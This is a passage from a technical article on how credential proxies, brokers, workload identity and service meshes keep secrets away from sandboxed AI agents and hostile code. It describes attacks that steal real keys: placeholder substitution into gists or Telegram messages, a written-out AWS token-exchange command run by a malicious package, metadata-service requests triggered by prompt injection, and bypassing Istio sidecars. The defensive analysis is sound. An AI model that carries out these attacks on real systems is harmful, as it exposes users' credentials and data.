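GitHub checks the token in the header, accepts the request and publishes the body, so the real token is now on a public page. The host list didn't prevent this because the request went to an approved host.

A commenter on Hacker News gave the gist example, and another asked whether creating a customer named `PLACEHOLDER` would produce a customer named after the secret. The secret can also end up in a comment, document or search query that the service stores or displays. A developer from Fly.io, posting as tptacek, replied that the answer depends on where the proxy allows the replacement, and called this "the big bug class" in the design.

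If the proxy replaces the placeholder only in the `Authorization` header, the request still succeeds, but the gist contains the worthless string. GitHub uses that header to decide whether to allow the request and doesn't publish it as content. (A service can still repeat a header in its response, which needs a separate defence.)

Replacing placeholders in request bodies can also expose a key when there is no attacker. When an agent runs `printenv`, it sends the output to its language model in the body of a request. If the output includes the placeholder for the model provider's key, the proxy inserts the real key into the conversation. The model can then repeat the key in a file, a commit or a command.

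Replacing the placeholder in any header is safer than replacing it in the body, but some services store headers too. Google Cloud Storage, for example, saves headers that begin with `x-goog-meta-` alongside an uploaded file and returns them to anyone who downloads it. Hostile code could put the placeholder in one of those headers. Docker's current custom secrets avoid this by having the proxy replace the placeholder only in headers the operator names. An earlier version replaced it anywhere in the request, which Docker presented as a way to handle secrets in bodies.

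Deno's behavior is less clear. Luca Casonato of Deno wrote in the Hacker News discussion that the proxy substitutes secrets only in headers, but according to an unsigned reply in a later copy of the thread, it also substitutes them in URL parameters and the body. Deno's documentation doesn't settle the question, so a customer should test it with a fake secret.

Infisical offers the widest choice of where to replace the placeholder. For each secret, the operator selects any combination of URL path, query string (the part of a URL after the question mark), headers and body. Infisical calls this selection "the security boundary". A Telegram bot token, for example, belongs in the path, so the operator should select only the path. If the operator also selects the query string, hostile code can call `sendMessage` with the placeholder as the message text and the attacker's chat as the recipient.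 Telegram then delivers the real token to the attacker. Infisical is replacing this product with Agent Vault, which can also swap a placeholder in the path or body, according to Infisical's *How Agent Vault Works*.

Blaxel, another sandbox provider, can insert credentials into request bodies in two ways. The operator can write a rule that adds a field to a request's JSON data, so the proxy determines where the secret goes. This works like header injection and is a good choice for services that accept a credential only in the body. Blaxel also replaces a placeholder such as `{{SECRET:api-token}}` when code in the sandbox writes it in a request's headers or body. The secret must belong to the rule for that destination, which keeps a Stripe key out of requests to OpenAI but doesn't stop hostile code from writing the Stripe key into a Stripe record. Blaxel calls the feature a public preview and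 advises against using it in production.

The sandbox tool microsandbox has safer defaults. According to *Sandboxes that lie about their secrets*, it replaces placeholders in headers, but replaces them in query strings and bodies only if the operator enables this.

| Product | What the program receives | Where the real secret can go |
|---|---|---|
| Docker, built-in services | `proxy-managed` | The authentication header, which the proxy overwrites |
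| Docker, local custom secrets | A random placeholder | Named headers, or a default list |
| Daytona | A random placeholder | Any header |
| Novita AI | A placeholder | Any header |
| Gondolin | A random placeholder | Any header, and the query string if enabled |
| microsandbox | A predictable placeholder by default | Headers, and the query string or body if enabled |
| Infisical | A random placeholder by default | Any combination of path, query string, headers and body |
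| Blaxel | A placeholder containing the secret's name | Headers and body |

A proxy that replaces a placeholder in a request's body must also correct the `Content-Length` header, which gives the body's size, because the real key is often longer or shorter than the placeholder. The proxy must also recognise the placeholder after the program has encoded it. HTTP Basic authentication, for example, joins a username and password, encodes them in Base64, a way of writing data as plain characters, and sends the result in a header. Daytona and Gondolin decode that header, replace the placeholder and encode the result again. Daytona doesn't undo other transformations. It also never replaces a placeholder in an unencrypted HTTP request, because the real secret would then cross the network in plain text.

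### When a guessable placeholder is dangerous

By default, microsandbox's *Secrets* forms a placeholder from `$MSB_` and the name of the environment variable, so anyone can guess that the placeholder for `GITHUB_TOKEN` is `$MSB_GITHUB_TOKEN`. Blaxel's placeholders contain a name the operator chose, which may be just as easy to guess.

Hostile code in a sandbox can read the placeholders for that sandbox's own secrets from the environment, so making them random does nothing to prevent the gist attack. Predictable placeholders are also harmless between sandboxes if the proxy first identifies the caller and searches only that caller's secrets.

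Guessing becomes a serious risk when several sandboxes share a proxy that looks up a secret by its placeholder alone. Code in one customer's sandbox could write another customer's placeholder, and the proxy would make the request with the other customer's key. A long random placeholder makes this impractical. With 128 random bits, usually written as 32 hexadecimal digits, the number of possible values is

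2^128 ≈ 3.4 × 10^38.

Suppose the proxy holds a million active placeholders and an attacker makes a billion guesses a second for a year, or about 3.2 × 10^16 guesses. The chance of finding even one placeholder is about

(3.2 × 10^16 × 10^6) / (3.4 × 10^38) ≈ 9 × 10^−17,

or roughly one in ten quadrillion. Deno's published example shows 48 hexadecimal digits before the text cuts off, which would be 192 bits if every digit is random. The calculation assumes a cryptographic random-number generator. A counter or timestamp of the same length would be easy to predict. Even a random placeholder can leak through a log or a prompt, so a shared proxy should still check which sandbox sent it.

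Guessable placeholder names are also dangerous when a trustworthy program handles text from strangers. For example, a shop's sandboxed program might copy customers' names from a web form into Stripe, through a proxy that replaces placeholders in request bodies. If a visitor enters `{{SECRET:stripe-key}}` as a name, the proxy inserts the real key and Stripe saves it as the customer's name. The key may then appear on the visitor's receipt, even though the visitor never ran any code in the sandbox. With a random placeholder, the visitor would have to learn the string first. If the proxy replaced placeholders only in the `Authorization` header, the visitor's text would reach Stripe unchanged.

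## Signing keys, OAuth logins and database passwords

Header injection and placeholders both put the secret into the request, so they only help when the request is supposed to contain it. An AWS client uses its secret key to compute a signature and sends only the signature. SSH and many databases work in a similar way, and an OAuth login delivers its secret in the service's reply. In all these cases, a trusted program outside the sandbox has to do part of the client's work.

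### Signing AWS requests

An AWS access key consists of an identifier, which the client sends with each request, and a secret key, which it doesn't send. AWS's signing method, Signature Version 4, uses an HMAC, a short code computed from a message and a secret key. Nobody can produce the right code without the key. AWS checks the code by repeating the client's calculation and comparing the results.

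To sign a request, the client first writes out its method, path, query string, chosen headers and a hash of the body in a standard form. It hashes that text and adds the time, date, region and service name, which gives the message to sign. It then derives a signing key:

```
k1 = HMAC("AWS4" + secret key, date)
k2 = HMAC(k1, region)
k3 = HMAC(k2, service)
signing key = HMAC(k3, "aws4_request")
```

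The HMAC of the message under this signing key is the signature, and the client puts it in the `Authorization` header:

```
Authorization: AWS4-HMAC-SHA256
  Credential=AKIA…/20261203/eu-west-1/s3/aws4_request,
  SignedHeaders=host;x-amz-content-sha256;x-amz-date,
  Signature=5d67…
```

A client with a fake secret key produces a well-formed but wrong signature, and the fake key appears nowhere in the request for a proxy to replace. The proxy has to make a new signature, in this order:

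1. Check the destination and remove the client's signature, timestamp and any session token.
2. Make every other change to the request, such as replacing placeholders or adding headers.
3. Hash the final body, set the current time and sign.
4. Send the request without changing it again.

If the proxy signs an upload to S3, Amazon's file storage, and then replaces a placeholder in the body, the body no longer matches the signed hash and S3 rejects the upload. S3 also rejects the upload if a second proxy later rewrites the path or a signed header. Nothing leaks, but the fault is hard to find because the key is correct.

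Large uploads are awkward because the proxy must read the whole body to compute its hash. S3 also accepts uploads in separately signed chunks, but those signatures are inside the body, and the proxy has to replace every one.

A stolen signature is much less useful to an attacker than a stolen bearer token, since it normally authorises one particular request for a few minutes. The proxy must still send each signed request only to the host it was signed for. Otherwise, hostile code could get the proxy to sign a request for S3 and deliver it to an attacker's server, and the attacker could forward it to S3. A presigned URL, which carries the signature in the address, can last for up to seven days and works for anyone who has it, so a broker that gives one to the sandbox is giving it a bearer credential for one operation.

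Not every credential proxy can sign requests. Fly.io's Tokenizer can compute an HMAC over selected parts of a request, according to *Tokenized Tokens*. The 11 built-in services Docker lists don't include AWS, and its custom secrets only replace a string in a header, which can't produce a signature. Without a signing proxy, the usual fallback is to give the sandbox short-lived AWS credentials from the platform.

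### Forwarding an SSH agent

Developers use SSH to log in to servers and often to push code with Git. SSH authenticates them with a key pair, and the private key is normally stored in a file that any program the developer runs can read. An SSH agent (unrelated to AI agents) is a program that holds private keys and signs with them on request. Other programs connect to it through a socket (a local connection point) and find the socket's location in the environment variable `SSH_AUTH_SOCK`.

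The host can forward this socket into the sandbox. When the coding agent pushes to GitHub, the SSH client in the sandbox connects to GitHub and the two agree on a session identifier. The client then passes the SSH agent a message containing that identifier. The SSH agent signs the message on the host, so the private key never enters the sandbox, and the client sends the signature to GitHub.

Docker turns on SSH agent forwarding by default when the host has an SSH agent, but environments in its newest format, v3, must also request the socket. An operator who doesn't need SSH can turn forwarding off with `ssh.agentForwardingEnabled`.

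While the socket is open, any process in the sandbox that can reach it can request signatures from any key in the SSH agent. Hostile code can therefore push to every repository and log in to every server that accepts one of those keys. It can also sign commits in the developer's name, if they sign commits with SSH. Closing the socket stops new signatures but doesn't undo the damage. Code that has logged in to a server may have added its own public key there, which would let it return without the SSH agent.

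Docker applies the sandbox's network rules to outbound SSH connections, but this restricts only connections that start in the sandbox. An attacker elsewhere can begin an SSH login to a server, send the message that needs signing to hostile code in the sandbox, and use the signature the code sends back. The attacker only needs a way to communicate with the sandbox, such as an ordinary web request.

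The simplest precaution is to run a separate SSH agent for the sandbox, with a single key that works for only one repository. OpenSSH, the most widely used SSH software, can also give a key a time limit, restrict it to named servers, or require the owner to confirm each use. Git can also use HTTPS instead of SSH, which lets an ordinary credential proxy add a token.

### CapSeal's broker for SSH and HTTP

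A broker can also run the SSH command itself, so the sandbox gets neither the key nor a socket that can sign with it. CapSeal, the research prototype that ties each permission to one session, works this way. Jin and colleagues rejected agent forwarding because they think limits on a forwarded signing service are hard to enforce.

The AI agent opens a session with the broker over a local socket, and the operating system identifies the calling process. The agent then asks for a capability, which is permission to perform one narrowly defined action. An SSH capability specifies the server, the user and an approved command prefix. It also limits the number of arguments and the size of the output, which is capped at 2,048 bytes in the paper's example. The broker checks the server's public key against a stored copy, so an attacker can't substitute a different server.

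If the policy allows the action, the broker returns a handle that works only in that session. Each request using the handle includes a sequence number, a one-time value and a timestamp, which the broker checks to reject repeats. It then runs the action, returns the output and records the event in a log designed to reveal tampering.

CapSeal treats HTTP in much the same way. A capability fixes the method, host and path, and describes the permitted structure of the body. The broker refuses any authorisation header from the agent and adds the real credential. This is stricter than a general credential proxy, but someone has to describe each permitted action in advance. Tools that rely on a forwarded SSH agent also need changes.

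Jin and colleagues tested CapSeal with scripted prompts and local HTTP and SSH servers. In trials that tried to extract the HTTP key, CapSeal never leaked it, while two comparison systems that gave the agent the key leaked it every time. None of the systems leaked an SSH key or used a credential outside its permitted scope, so the tests provide no evidence that CapSeal prevents either. CapSeal added about 0.15 milliseconds to the median HTTP request and 0.21 milliseconds to the median SSH command, excluding SSH connection setup.

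Jin and colleagues did not test SSH to remote hosts, and their prototype doesn't include hardware-backed secret storage. They leave attacks through poisoned tool descriptions to a separate experiment. The paper also describes running the broker in a protected area of the processor and using it for connected devices, but reports no tests of either.

### OAuth logins and token refresh

With OAuth, the user approves a program in a browser, and the service issues a short-lived authorisation code. The program sends this code to an address called the token endpoint and receives an access token and a refresh token. The access token authenticates requests, often for about an hour, and the program can use the refresh token to get new access tokens for much longer. A proxy that edits only requests would leave both tokens in the reply, so they would reach the sandbox.

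The safest solution is to log in outside the sandbox. Fly.io wrote a program called SSOkenizer because its web application would otherwise have briefly handled each new token at login. SSOkenizer completes the login, seals the token for Tokenizer and gives the application only the sealed version. Docker has a command that runs the login for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, on the host.

Other agents, including Claude Code, ask the user to log in from inside the sandbox. For these, Docker intercepts the token endpoint's reply. Suppose the service returns this:

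```
{"access_token": "eyJ…", "refresh_token": "rt_…", "expires_in": 3600}
```

The proxy keeps the real tokens and passes on harmless substitutes:

```
{"access_token": "fake-access", "refresh_token": "fake-refresh", "expires_in": 3600}
```

The agent saves the substitutes as if they were real, and the proxy puts the real access token into requests to the service's approved hosts. When the access token expires, the agent sends `fake-refresh` to the token endpoint. The proxy replaces it with the real refresh token, stores the new tokens and again returns substitutes. Docker's proxy refuses any token exchange over unencrypted HTTP.

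Some services issue a new refresh token at every refresh and cancel the old one. The proxy must save the new token immediately, or the user will have to log in again. If several sandboxes share one login, the proxy should allow only one refresh at a time, because the service may treat a second attempt with the old token as theft and end the login.

Hostile code can also bypass interception when the authorisation code passes through the sandbox. It can send the authorisation code to an attacker, together with any one-time value the client created for the login. The attacker can then use another machine to exchange them for real tokens, and the reply never passes through the proxy. The authorisation code works once and expires within minutes, but an automated attack needs only seconds. Logging in on the host avoids this.

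Docker documents several cases in which real tokens enter the sandbox. An environment's configuration can set `passthrough: true`, which delivers the token reply to the sandbox unchanged. According to Docker's *Authenticate cloud agents*, an agent's own login can write credentials to files in a cloud sandbox. Those files can end up in templates and in the snapshots Docker takes when it moves a sandbox, so a token may spread to copies the developer has forgotten. Docker advises signing out and removing the credentials before capturing or moving the sandbox.

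OAuth handling also changes between versions. In August 2026, Docker warned that its proxy did not manage OAuth for third-party agents, including modified versions of its built-in ones, and that logging in inside the sandbox stored the real token there. By December, Docker had removed the warning and explained how to declare OAuth for a custom environment. Someone running an older version can check whether the sandbox holds the real token by logging in with a test account and inspecting the credential file.

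### Database passwords

Most databases use their own protocols instead of HTTP, and many never send the password itself. PostgreSQL, for example, normally uses SCRAM, in which the client proves it knows the password by combining it with random values from both sides. A program with a placeholder would compute the wrong proof, and the proxy would find no placeholder to replace.

A protocol broker solves this by logging in to the database for the program. The program connects to the broker with a dummy password or none. The broker opens an encrypted connection to the database, checks the server's certificate and completes the login with the real password. It then reports success to the program and passes messages between the program and the database. CyberArk's Secretless Broker, an early open-source example, does this for PostgreSQL, MySQL and Microsoft SQL Server. Before adopting it, an operator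 should check that the project still receives security fixes.

Once the broker has logged in, hostile code can run any command that the database account permits. In PostgreSQL, an ordinary account can change its own password, so the code could set a new one and later log in without the broker. The database should accept logins to that account only from the broker's network address.

Some databases accept logins over HTTP, so a web proxy can handle those logins if it can parse their format. Vercel's *How v0 authenticates to Snowflake without exposing the user's OAuth token* describes this approach for v0, which generates applications with a language model. Snowflake, a cloud database, accepts the user's token in a header for some requests and in a field of a JSON login message for others.

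Vercel's first proxy replaced a placeholder with the real token anywhere in the request body, the same flaw as in the gist example. Generated code could have run a query such as `SELECT '<placeholder>'`, and the database would have returned the real token. The current proxy parses the login message, writes the token only into the login field, and rejects the request if the placeholder appears anywhere else. It also handles refreshes on the server, using the user session linked to that sandbox.

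After login, Snowflake issues a session token that does enter the sandbox. Vercel's helper code closes the connection after each query, which ends the session, but hostile code could keep a session open. By default, Snowflake ends a session after four hours of inactivity. Someone who stole the session token could access the database for a while, but would not have the user's reusable OAuth token.

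In its first 15 days, the proxy added credentials to about 13,000 requests and rejected none for misusing the placeholder. These figures show that ordinary clients work through the proxy, but they are little evidence of how it would withstand an attack, since nobody appears to have attacked it.

### The Agent Authenticator proposal

Most of these arrangements still depend on a secret that an attacker could steal from the proxy or broker. *Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, November 2026) proposes replacing such secrets with private keys that never leave secure hardware. The design adapts passkeys, which let people log in to websites with a key held on their phone or computer.

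A separate program, the authenticator, would hold a different key for each service. The software that launches the AI agent would read the service's name from the live connection, so a prompt injection could not obtain a signature for one service and use it at another. A person would use their own passkey to sign a mandate, which lists the services the agent may use, the actions it may take and when its permission expires. High-risk actions, such as publishing a package, would need a new approval on the person's phone or other device.

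After checking the agent's signature, the service would issue a short-lived access token tied to the agent's key. Each request would need proof that the sender holds that key, so a stolen token would be useless without it. Ganesan also proposes ways to connect the design to OAuth, Git and SSH. A service that supports none of them would still require an ordinary token, which the authenticator could get through a broker and keep away from the model.

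Ganesan judged from incident reports that the design would have blocked or contained five real attacks, but has not built a full version and reports no measurements. Secure hardware stops a key from being copied, but most desktop operating systems can't reliably prove which process asked for a signature. Malicious code on the same machine might therefore be able to request one, much as it can through a forwarded SSH socket. The design relies on human approval to stop such code from getting high-risk actions signed, although Ganesan acknowledges the risk of approval fatigue.

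## Workload identity and service meshes

Credential proxies and brokers keep a secret away from the untrusted program, but someone still has to store, protect and replace the secret. Workload identity can remove the need for a stored secret. The platform that runs a program can check which machine the program is on and how it started, use this information to identify the program, and issue it a credential that expires within minutes or hours.

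The service that receives the credential has to trust the platform. An operator can usually set up this trust with a cloud provider or with the company's own internal services. An outside service that accepts only its own API keys still needs one of the earlier arrangements.

### How SPIRE proves what a program is

SPIFFE is an open standard for naming programs and proving their names, and SPIRE is open-source software that implements it. A SPIFFE name looks like a web address:

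`spiffe://example.com/builds/coding-agent`

A program proves its name with an SVID (SPIFFE Verifiable Identity Document), which is either an X.509 certificate or a JWT (JSON Web Token). The certificate, the kind that web servers use, comes with a private key, which the program proves it has each time it connects. The JWT is a short signed text that serves as a bearer credential.

SPIRE consists of a central server, which signs SVIDs, and a SPIRE agent on each machine (unrelated to AI agents). The operator first registers each program by pairing its name with selectors, the properties a process must have to receive that name:

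```
SPIFFE ID:  spiffe://example.com/builds/coding-agent
Selectors:  k8s:ns:builds
            k8s:sa:coding-agent
```

These selectors require the process to run in the Kubernetes namespace `builds` (a namespace is a named division of a cluster) under the service account `coding-agent`. A service account is an identity that Kubernetes gives to programs instead of people. SPIFFE's *SPIRE Concepts* describes what happens next on an AWS virtual machine:

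1. The SPIRE agent obtains a document from AWS that identifies the virtual machine, and sends it to the SPIRE server.
2. The server checks the document with AWS and gives the SPIRE agent an SVID of its own. This completes the attestation, or proof of identity, of the machine.
3. The server sends the SPIRE agent only the registrations that apply to that machine. The SPIRE agent requests a certificate for each one and keeps the results ready.
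4. A program asks for its identity through a local socket. It presents no password. The SPIRE agent asks the operating system for the process ID of the caller.
5. The SPIRE agent uses the process ID to look up the caller's properties, such as its user account or its Kubernetes service account. This is the attestation of the process.
6. The SPIRE agent compares those properties with the registered selectors and returns the matching SVID.

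Machines outside a cloud can prove their identity with a key in a security chip or with a single-use join token. According to Palo Alto Networks, the program receives a private key and the certificates it needs to check other programs, and the system renews certificates before they expire without restarting the program. SPIRE's default lifetimes are one hour for a certificate and five minutes for a JWT.

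### Exchanging a Kubernetes token for AWS credentials

Cloud providers have their own version of this process. Suppose the coding agent runs in a Kubernetes pod on EKS, Amazon's managed Kubernetes service, and has to read test data from S3. Kubernetes gives the pod a service-account token, a JWT with contents like these:

```
{
  "iss": "https://oidc.eks.eu-west-1.amazonaws.com/id/…",
  "sub": "system:serviceaccount:builds:coding-agent",
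  "aud": ["sts.amazonaws.com"],
  "iat": 1796295600,
  "exp": 1796299200
}
```

The `iss` field names the cluster that issued the token, and `sub` names the service account. The audience, `aud`, is the only recipient that should accept the token. The last two fields give the times of issue and expiry in seconds, here 3,600 seconds apart. The exchange then has five steps:

1. The kubelet, the Kubernetes program that manages each machine, requests the token on the pod's behalf and writes it to a file in the pod. Under Kubernetes' *KEP-1205*, the design document for these tokens, the token must also name the pod.
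2. The AWS library in the program reads the file and sends the token to AWS, along with the name of a role, which is a set of AWS permissions. AWS's *IAM roles for service accounts* names this operation `AssumeRoleWithWebIdentity`.
3. AWS checks the signature against public keys that EKS publishes. It also checks the expiry time, the audience and whether the role accepts this service account.
4. AWS returns a temporary access key, secret key and session token.
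5. The library repeats the exchange before the temporary credentials expire.

Nobody has to create or store an AWS key for the program. EKS replaces its own signing key every seven days. Service-account tokens last one hour by default, according to AWS and the blog post *Kubernetes service account tokens*, which also gives a minimum of ten minutes. The temporary AWS credentials also last an hour by default, according to another post, *Securing EKS Workloads*. Operators can change these values, but a token's `exp` field shows when it actually expires.

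With these defaults, a thief could copy a new service-account token, exchange it just before it expires and use the resulting AWS credentials for another hour, so the theft would remain useful for almost two hours. The thief can also request a longer AWS session, up to the role's limit, which an administrator can set as high as 12 hours. Deleting the pod doesn't prevent the exchange, because AWS checks the token's signature and expiry but not whether the pod still exists.

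A newer alternative, EKS Pod Identity, attaches labels to the temporary credentials, including the cluster, namespace and service account. According to AWS, an administrator can then write one role that gives each program access only to resources with a matching label, which makes narrow permissions easier to maintain.

### Code running as the workload can request the credential

Workload identity removes the stored secret, but it does not by itself keep credentials away from hostile code. Kubernetes' *Managing Service Accounts* explains that a process inside a pod can use the identity of the pod's service account. The installation script of a malicious package is such a process. On EKS it can carry out the whole exchange with one ordinary command:

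```
aws sts assume-role-with-web-identity \
  --role-arn "$AWS_ROLE_ARN" \
  --role-session-name build \
  --web-identity-token "$(cat $AWS_WEB_IDENTITY_TOKEN_FILE)"
```

The command prints working AWS credentials, and the script can send them anywhere the network allows.

SPIRE can be more selective because it examines the process requesting an identity. But the example selectors match every process in any pod that runs under that service account, and a selector for a user account matches everything that user runs. A selector for the program's file path would exclude a shell that the agent starts, but not a malicious Python package. Python runs a package in the same process as the program that imports it, so the operating system can't distinguish the package from the program.

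The short lifetime is still useful because owners often leave leaked credentials working for years, while a one-hour credential expires by itself. This may be enough protection for a nightly job written by trusted employees, but not for an AI agent that reads text from strangers, because an hour gives an attacker plenty of time to copy a database.

### The metadata service

A cloud virtual machine gets its identity from a metadata service, a web service at a fixed address that only the machine can reach. On AWS and several other clouds, the address is `169.254.169.254`. A program on the machine can request the machine's name, network settings and, if the operator has given the machine a role, temporary credentials for that role. The program needs no password because the metadata service treats any request from the machine as authorised.

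This is dangerous when the machine runs a sandbox. AWS's *Diving into IAM Roles for Service Accounts* describes the instance profile, the role attached to a virtual machine, as the identity a container falls back on when it has no AWS credentials of its own. So even if an operator removes every secret from a sandbox, code inside it can still get a credential with one web request, and a prompt injection only has to make the agent fetch a particular address. The machine's role may also be broader than any single container needs, since it serves all of them.

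IMDSv2, the current version of AWS's instance metadata service, requires the caller to first obtain a session token with a `PUT` request. This blocks many attacks in which an outsider tricks a web server into fetching an address but cannot choose the HTTP method. But code in a sandbox can send both requests itself. IMDSv2 also limits how many network hops its replies can travel, which can keep them from reaching a container, depending on the container's network setup.

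The reliable approach is to block the sandbox from reaching the address. The credential proxy must also refuse requests for it, or hostile code could ask the proxy to fetch the address and receive the credentials of the proxy's host machine. Blocking the address does not remove a service-account token from the pod's files, so the sandbox also needs a service account with no cloud role.

### Giving the identity to the proxy

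Operators can keep workload identity away from untrusted code by giving it to the proxy instead. In the S3 example, the coding agent runs under a service account with no AWS permissions. A signing proxy runs in another pod, under a service account that can read the test data. The proxy exchanges its own token for temporary credentials and uses them to sign the agent's requests. Nobody stores an AWS key, and running `printenv` in the sandbox shows no usable credentials.

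The proxy should have its own pod because a pod has only one service account, and by default Kubernetes puts that account's token in every container in the pod. If the agent and the proxy share a pod, the operator has to turn off this default and mount the token only in the proxy's container.

Hostile code can still misuse the credentials through the proxy, but it can no longer take them elsewhere, and its access ends when the operator stops the sandbox.

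### Tying a token to a key

Another way is to make the token useless without a private key that the program can't copy. OAuth has two published standards for this. One, RFC 8705 (2020), uses mutual TLS, in which both sides of a connection present certificates. The access token contains a fingerprint of the client's certificate, and the service refuses the token if the fingerprint doesn't match the certificate on the current connection.

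DPoP (Demonstrating Proof of Possession), which RFC 9449 defined in 2023, works at the level of individual requests. The access token contains a fingerprint of the client's public key. With each request, the client sends a small signed statement, or proof, such as this:

```
{
  "htm": "POST",
  "htu": "https://api.example.com/reports",
  "iat": 1796295600,
  "jti": "a91c…",
  "ath": "fUHy…"
}
```

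The proof contains the request's method and address, the time, a unique identifier and a hash of the access token. The service checks the proof's signature against the key named in the access token and can reject a proof whose identifier it has already seen. A thief who finds the access token in a log cannot make a valid proof, and a copied proof works only briefly and only for the same method and address.

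All of this depends on where the private key is. If the key is in a file beside the token, a malicious package will take both. If secure hardware or a separate process holds the key, hostile code can't copy it but may still be able to request signatures, as with a forwarded SSH socket. The code could also collect DPoP proofs dated in the future and send them to an attacker. A service can prevent this by requiring each proof to include a random value it recently issued.

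Ganesan's Agent Authenticator, which uses DPoP, ranks the protection of agents' keys on a four-level scale. Cloud workload identity alone ranks second-lowest, below keys in dedicated secure hardware. Ganesan also notes that workload identity doesn't provide for a person's approval and suits laptops poorly, because no cloud platform can vouch for the machine.

Few services used by agents are ready for key-bound tokens. Ganesan cites an analysis of 5,205 open-source servers for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common way to connect AI agents to outside tools. About 53% relied on fixed API keys or personal access tokens, and only 8.5% used OAuth. Mutual TLS also conflicts with TLS interception, because a proxy that ends the client's connection must present its own certificate to the real service and hold the key for it.

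### How a service mesh handles keys

A service mesh sets up mutual TLS between a company's services without changes to their code. In Istio, a widely used open-source mesh, each pod can have a sidecar that runs Envoy, a general-purpose proxy. Network rules in the pod redirect the application's connections to the sidecar.

If the coding agent calls an internal service at `http://test-results/`, it sends an ordinary unencrypted request. The sidecar encrypts the request and presents the pod's certificate. At the other end, the sidecar of `test-results` checks the certificate, applies its access rules and passes the unencrypted request to its own application. The private keys stay in the sidecars, which get them as follows:

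1. Envoy asks for a certificate through its secret discovery service (SDS), a protocol for delivering keys and certificates to a running proxy. In Istio, a helper program beside Envoy answers the request.
2. The helper creates a private key and sends the matching public key to Istio's central server, istiod. It proves the pod's identity with a service-account token.
3. Istiod checks the token with Kubernetes and signs a certificate for that identity only.
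4. The helper passes the certificate and private key to Envoy. Istio repeats the process periodically to replace both.

Envoy's *Secret discovery service (SDS)* explains that a proxy using SDS switches to a new certificate immediately. Without SDS, operators would have to place certificates in the proxy's container and redeploy it whenever one expired. SPIRE can supply the certificates in place of Istio's helper. If Envoy can't fetch a client certificate it needs, it rejects the requests that depend on it rather than sending the data unencrypted.

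Two of Istio's defaults weaken the arrangement. Sidecars accept unencrypted connections as well as mutual TLS until the operator selects strict mode. Istio also doesn't restrict which services a caller can reach by default, since mutual TLS only identifies the caller. Istio's *Security Best Practices* warns that anyone with a valid certificate can reach a service unless an authorisation policy forbids it.

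### Envoy's credential injector

GitHub doesn't accept certificates from a company's mesh, so a request to GitHub still needs a token. Envoy's *Credential injector* describes a component that adds the credential to the request's header. The credential can be a stored value or a short-lived OAuth token. Envoy holds a client ID and secret and exchanges them for the OAuth token at the service's token endpoint.

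The component authenticates the program behind the proxy, not the person using it. If one agent service works for 50 employees, an outside service receives the same identity with every request and can't set permissions for each employee.

As in Modal's example, the program sends plain HTTP to the proxy, which opens the encrypted connection to the outside service. Istio warns that the operator must carefully configure which certificate authorities and server name the proxy accepts on that connection. A mistake could send the token to an impostor.

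Another setting, `overwrite`, determines whether Envoy replaces a header that the program supplies itself. Envoy Gateway's *Credential Injection*, a guide to using the component at a shared gateway, says that Envoy keeps the existing header unless the operator sets `overwrite` to true. The default therefore lets through a token for the attacker's own account. Envoy counts the requests that kept their own header, so an operator can check whether programs are supplying one.

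Envoy's sample configuration also sets `allow_request_without_credential` to true, which lets a request continue when the proxy has no credential to add. For untrusted code, the operator should set it to false so that a missing secret causes an error. Otherwise, a request could go out with whatever header the program wrote.

### Keeping keys in a proxy for each machine

Istio also has an ambient mode, which replaces the sidecars with one proxy per machine, called the ztunnel. *Ambient Mode Security Deep Dive* (Jackson, Kohavi and colleagues, 2022) explains the security reasons for this design. With a sidecar, an attacker who takes over the application also gets the sidecar and its keys. The ztunnel runs outside the application's pod, so the same attacker gets no keys.

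The drawback is that one ztunnel holds the keys of every pod on its machine. Jackson and colleagues, who worked at Google and Solo.io, two companies that develop Istio, consider this acceptable for two reasons. The ztunnel can obtain certificates only for pods running on its own machine, and it doesn't interpret HTTP, the source of most of Envoy's past vulnerabilities. The trade-off looks good for untrusted code. A sidecar keeps its key in the same pod as the hostile code, whereas that code would have to exploit a flaw in the ztunnel or the machine to reach a key the ztunnel holds.

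SPIRE also works with this design. *Kubernetes Identity the Right Way with SPIRE and Ambient* describes a setup in which the ztunnel collects SPIRE certificates for the pods, so the operator doesn't have to give each pod access to SPIRE's socket.

The ztunnel doesn't interpret HTTP, so it can't add an `Authorization` header. Istio uses a separate waypoint proxy for HTTP processing, which serves one or more services and has its own identity.

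| Proxy | Private keys it holds | Can it work with HTTP headers? | What an attacker gains by taking it over |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sidecar | One pod's | Yes | That pod's identity and any credentials the sidecar adds |
| Ztunnel | Those of every pod on its machine | No | The identity of every pod on that machine |
| Waypoint | Its own | Yes | The traffic of the services it handles, but not their identities |

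### Whether a mesh contains hostile code

Operators cannot rely on an Istio sidecar to contain a hostile program, even though the mesh encrypts traffic, checks identities and can log every connection. Istio's *Security Model* tells operators to assume that an attacker who controls an application also controls its sidecar. The attacker may be able to extract the sidecar's private key and use it elsewhere, or bypass the sidecar and send traffic directly.

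Istio describes several ways to bypass the sidecar. The redirection covers only TCP, so a program can send data around the proxy over UDP. Operators sometimes exempt particular ports from redirection. A program with enough rights in the pod can remove the redirection rules or replace the proxy. Envoy's debugging interface listens on port 15000 of `localhost`, which the application shares. Modal avoided a similar weakness in its own sidecar by turning off Caddy's administration interface.

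A process can also escape the redirection if it can switch to the user account that Istio exempts. Istio uses this exemption for the sidecar's own outbound traffic, which would otherwise loop back to the sidecar forever.

Istio guarantees that a program cannot bypass another pod's sidecar. If `test-results` accepts requests only from the build system, a hostile program elsewhere in the mesh can't avoid that check. A mesh therefore protects internal services well from a compromised pod, but a sidecar alone can't stop that pod from sending source code to the internet.

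Many operators use the setting `REGISTRY_ONLY`, which makes sidecars refuse connections to undeclared destinations. The Istio project says this is not a security control, though it is commonly mistaken for one. The setting blocks accidental connections, but a program can avoid the restriction by bypassing its sidecar.

For stronger control of outbound traffic, Istio recommends an egress gateway, a separate proxy through which all traffic leaves the mesh. The gateway runs in its own pod, so the hostile program can't alter it. Google Cloud's *Best Practices for using Cloud Service Mesh egress gateways on GKE clusters* describes controls that limit connections by source application and destination. But the sidecar directs traffic to the gateway, so a program that bypasses the sidecar also bypasses the gateway. Istio's *Egress Gateways* states that Istio cannot securely force traffic through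 the gateway, so something outside the mesh has to block every other route.

In Kubernetes, that can be a NetworkPolicy, a rule about which connections a pod may make. Istio's guide demonstrates the difference with a pod that has no sidecar, which stands in for a program that has bypassed one:

1. The pod requests a page from CNN's website directly and gets it, even though a gateway is in place.
2. The operator adds a NetworkPolicy that lets pods in that namespace reach only the cluster's DNS service, Istio's own components and the gateway.
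3. The pod repeats the request, and the connection times out.
4. The operator gives the pod a sidecar, which directs the request to the gateway, and the request succeeds.

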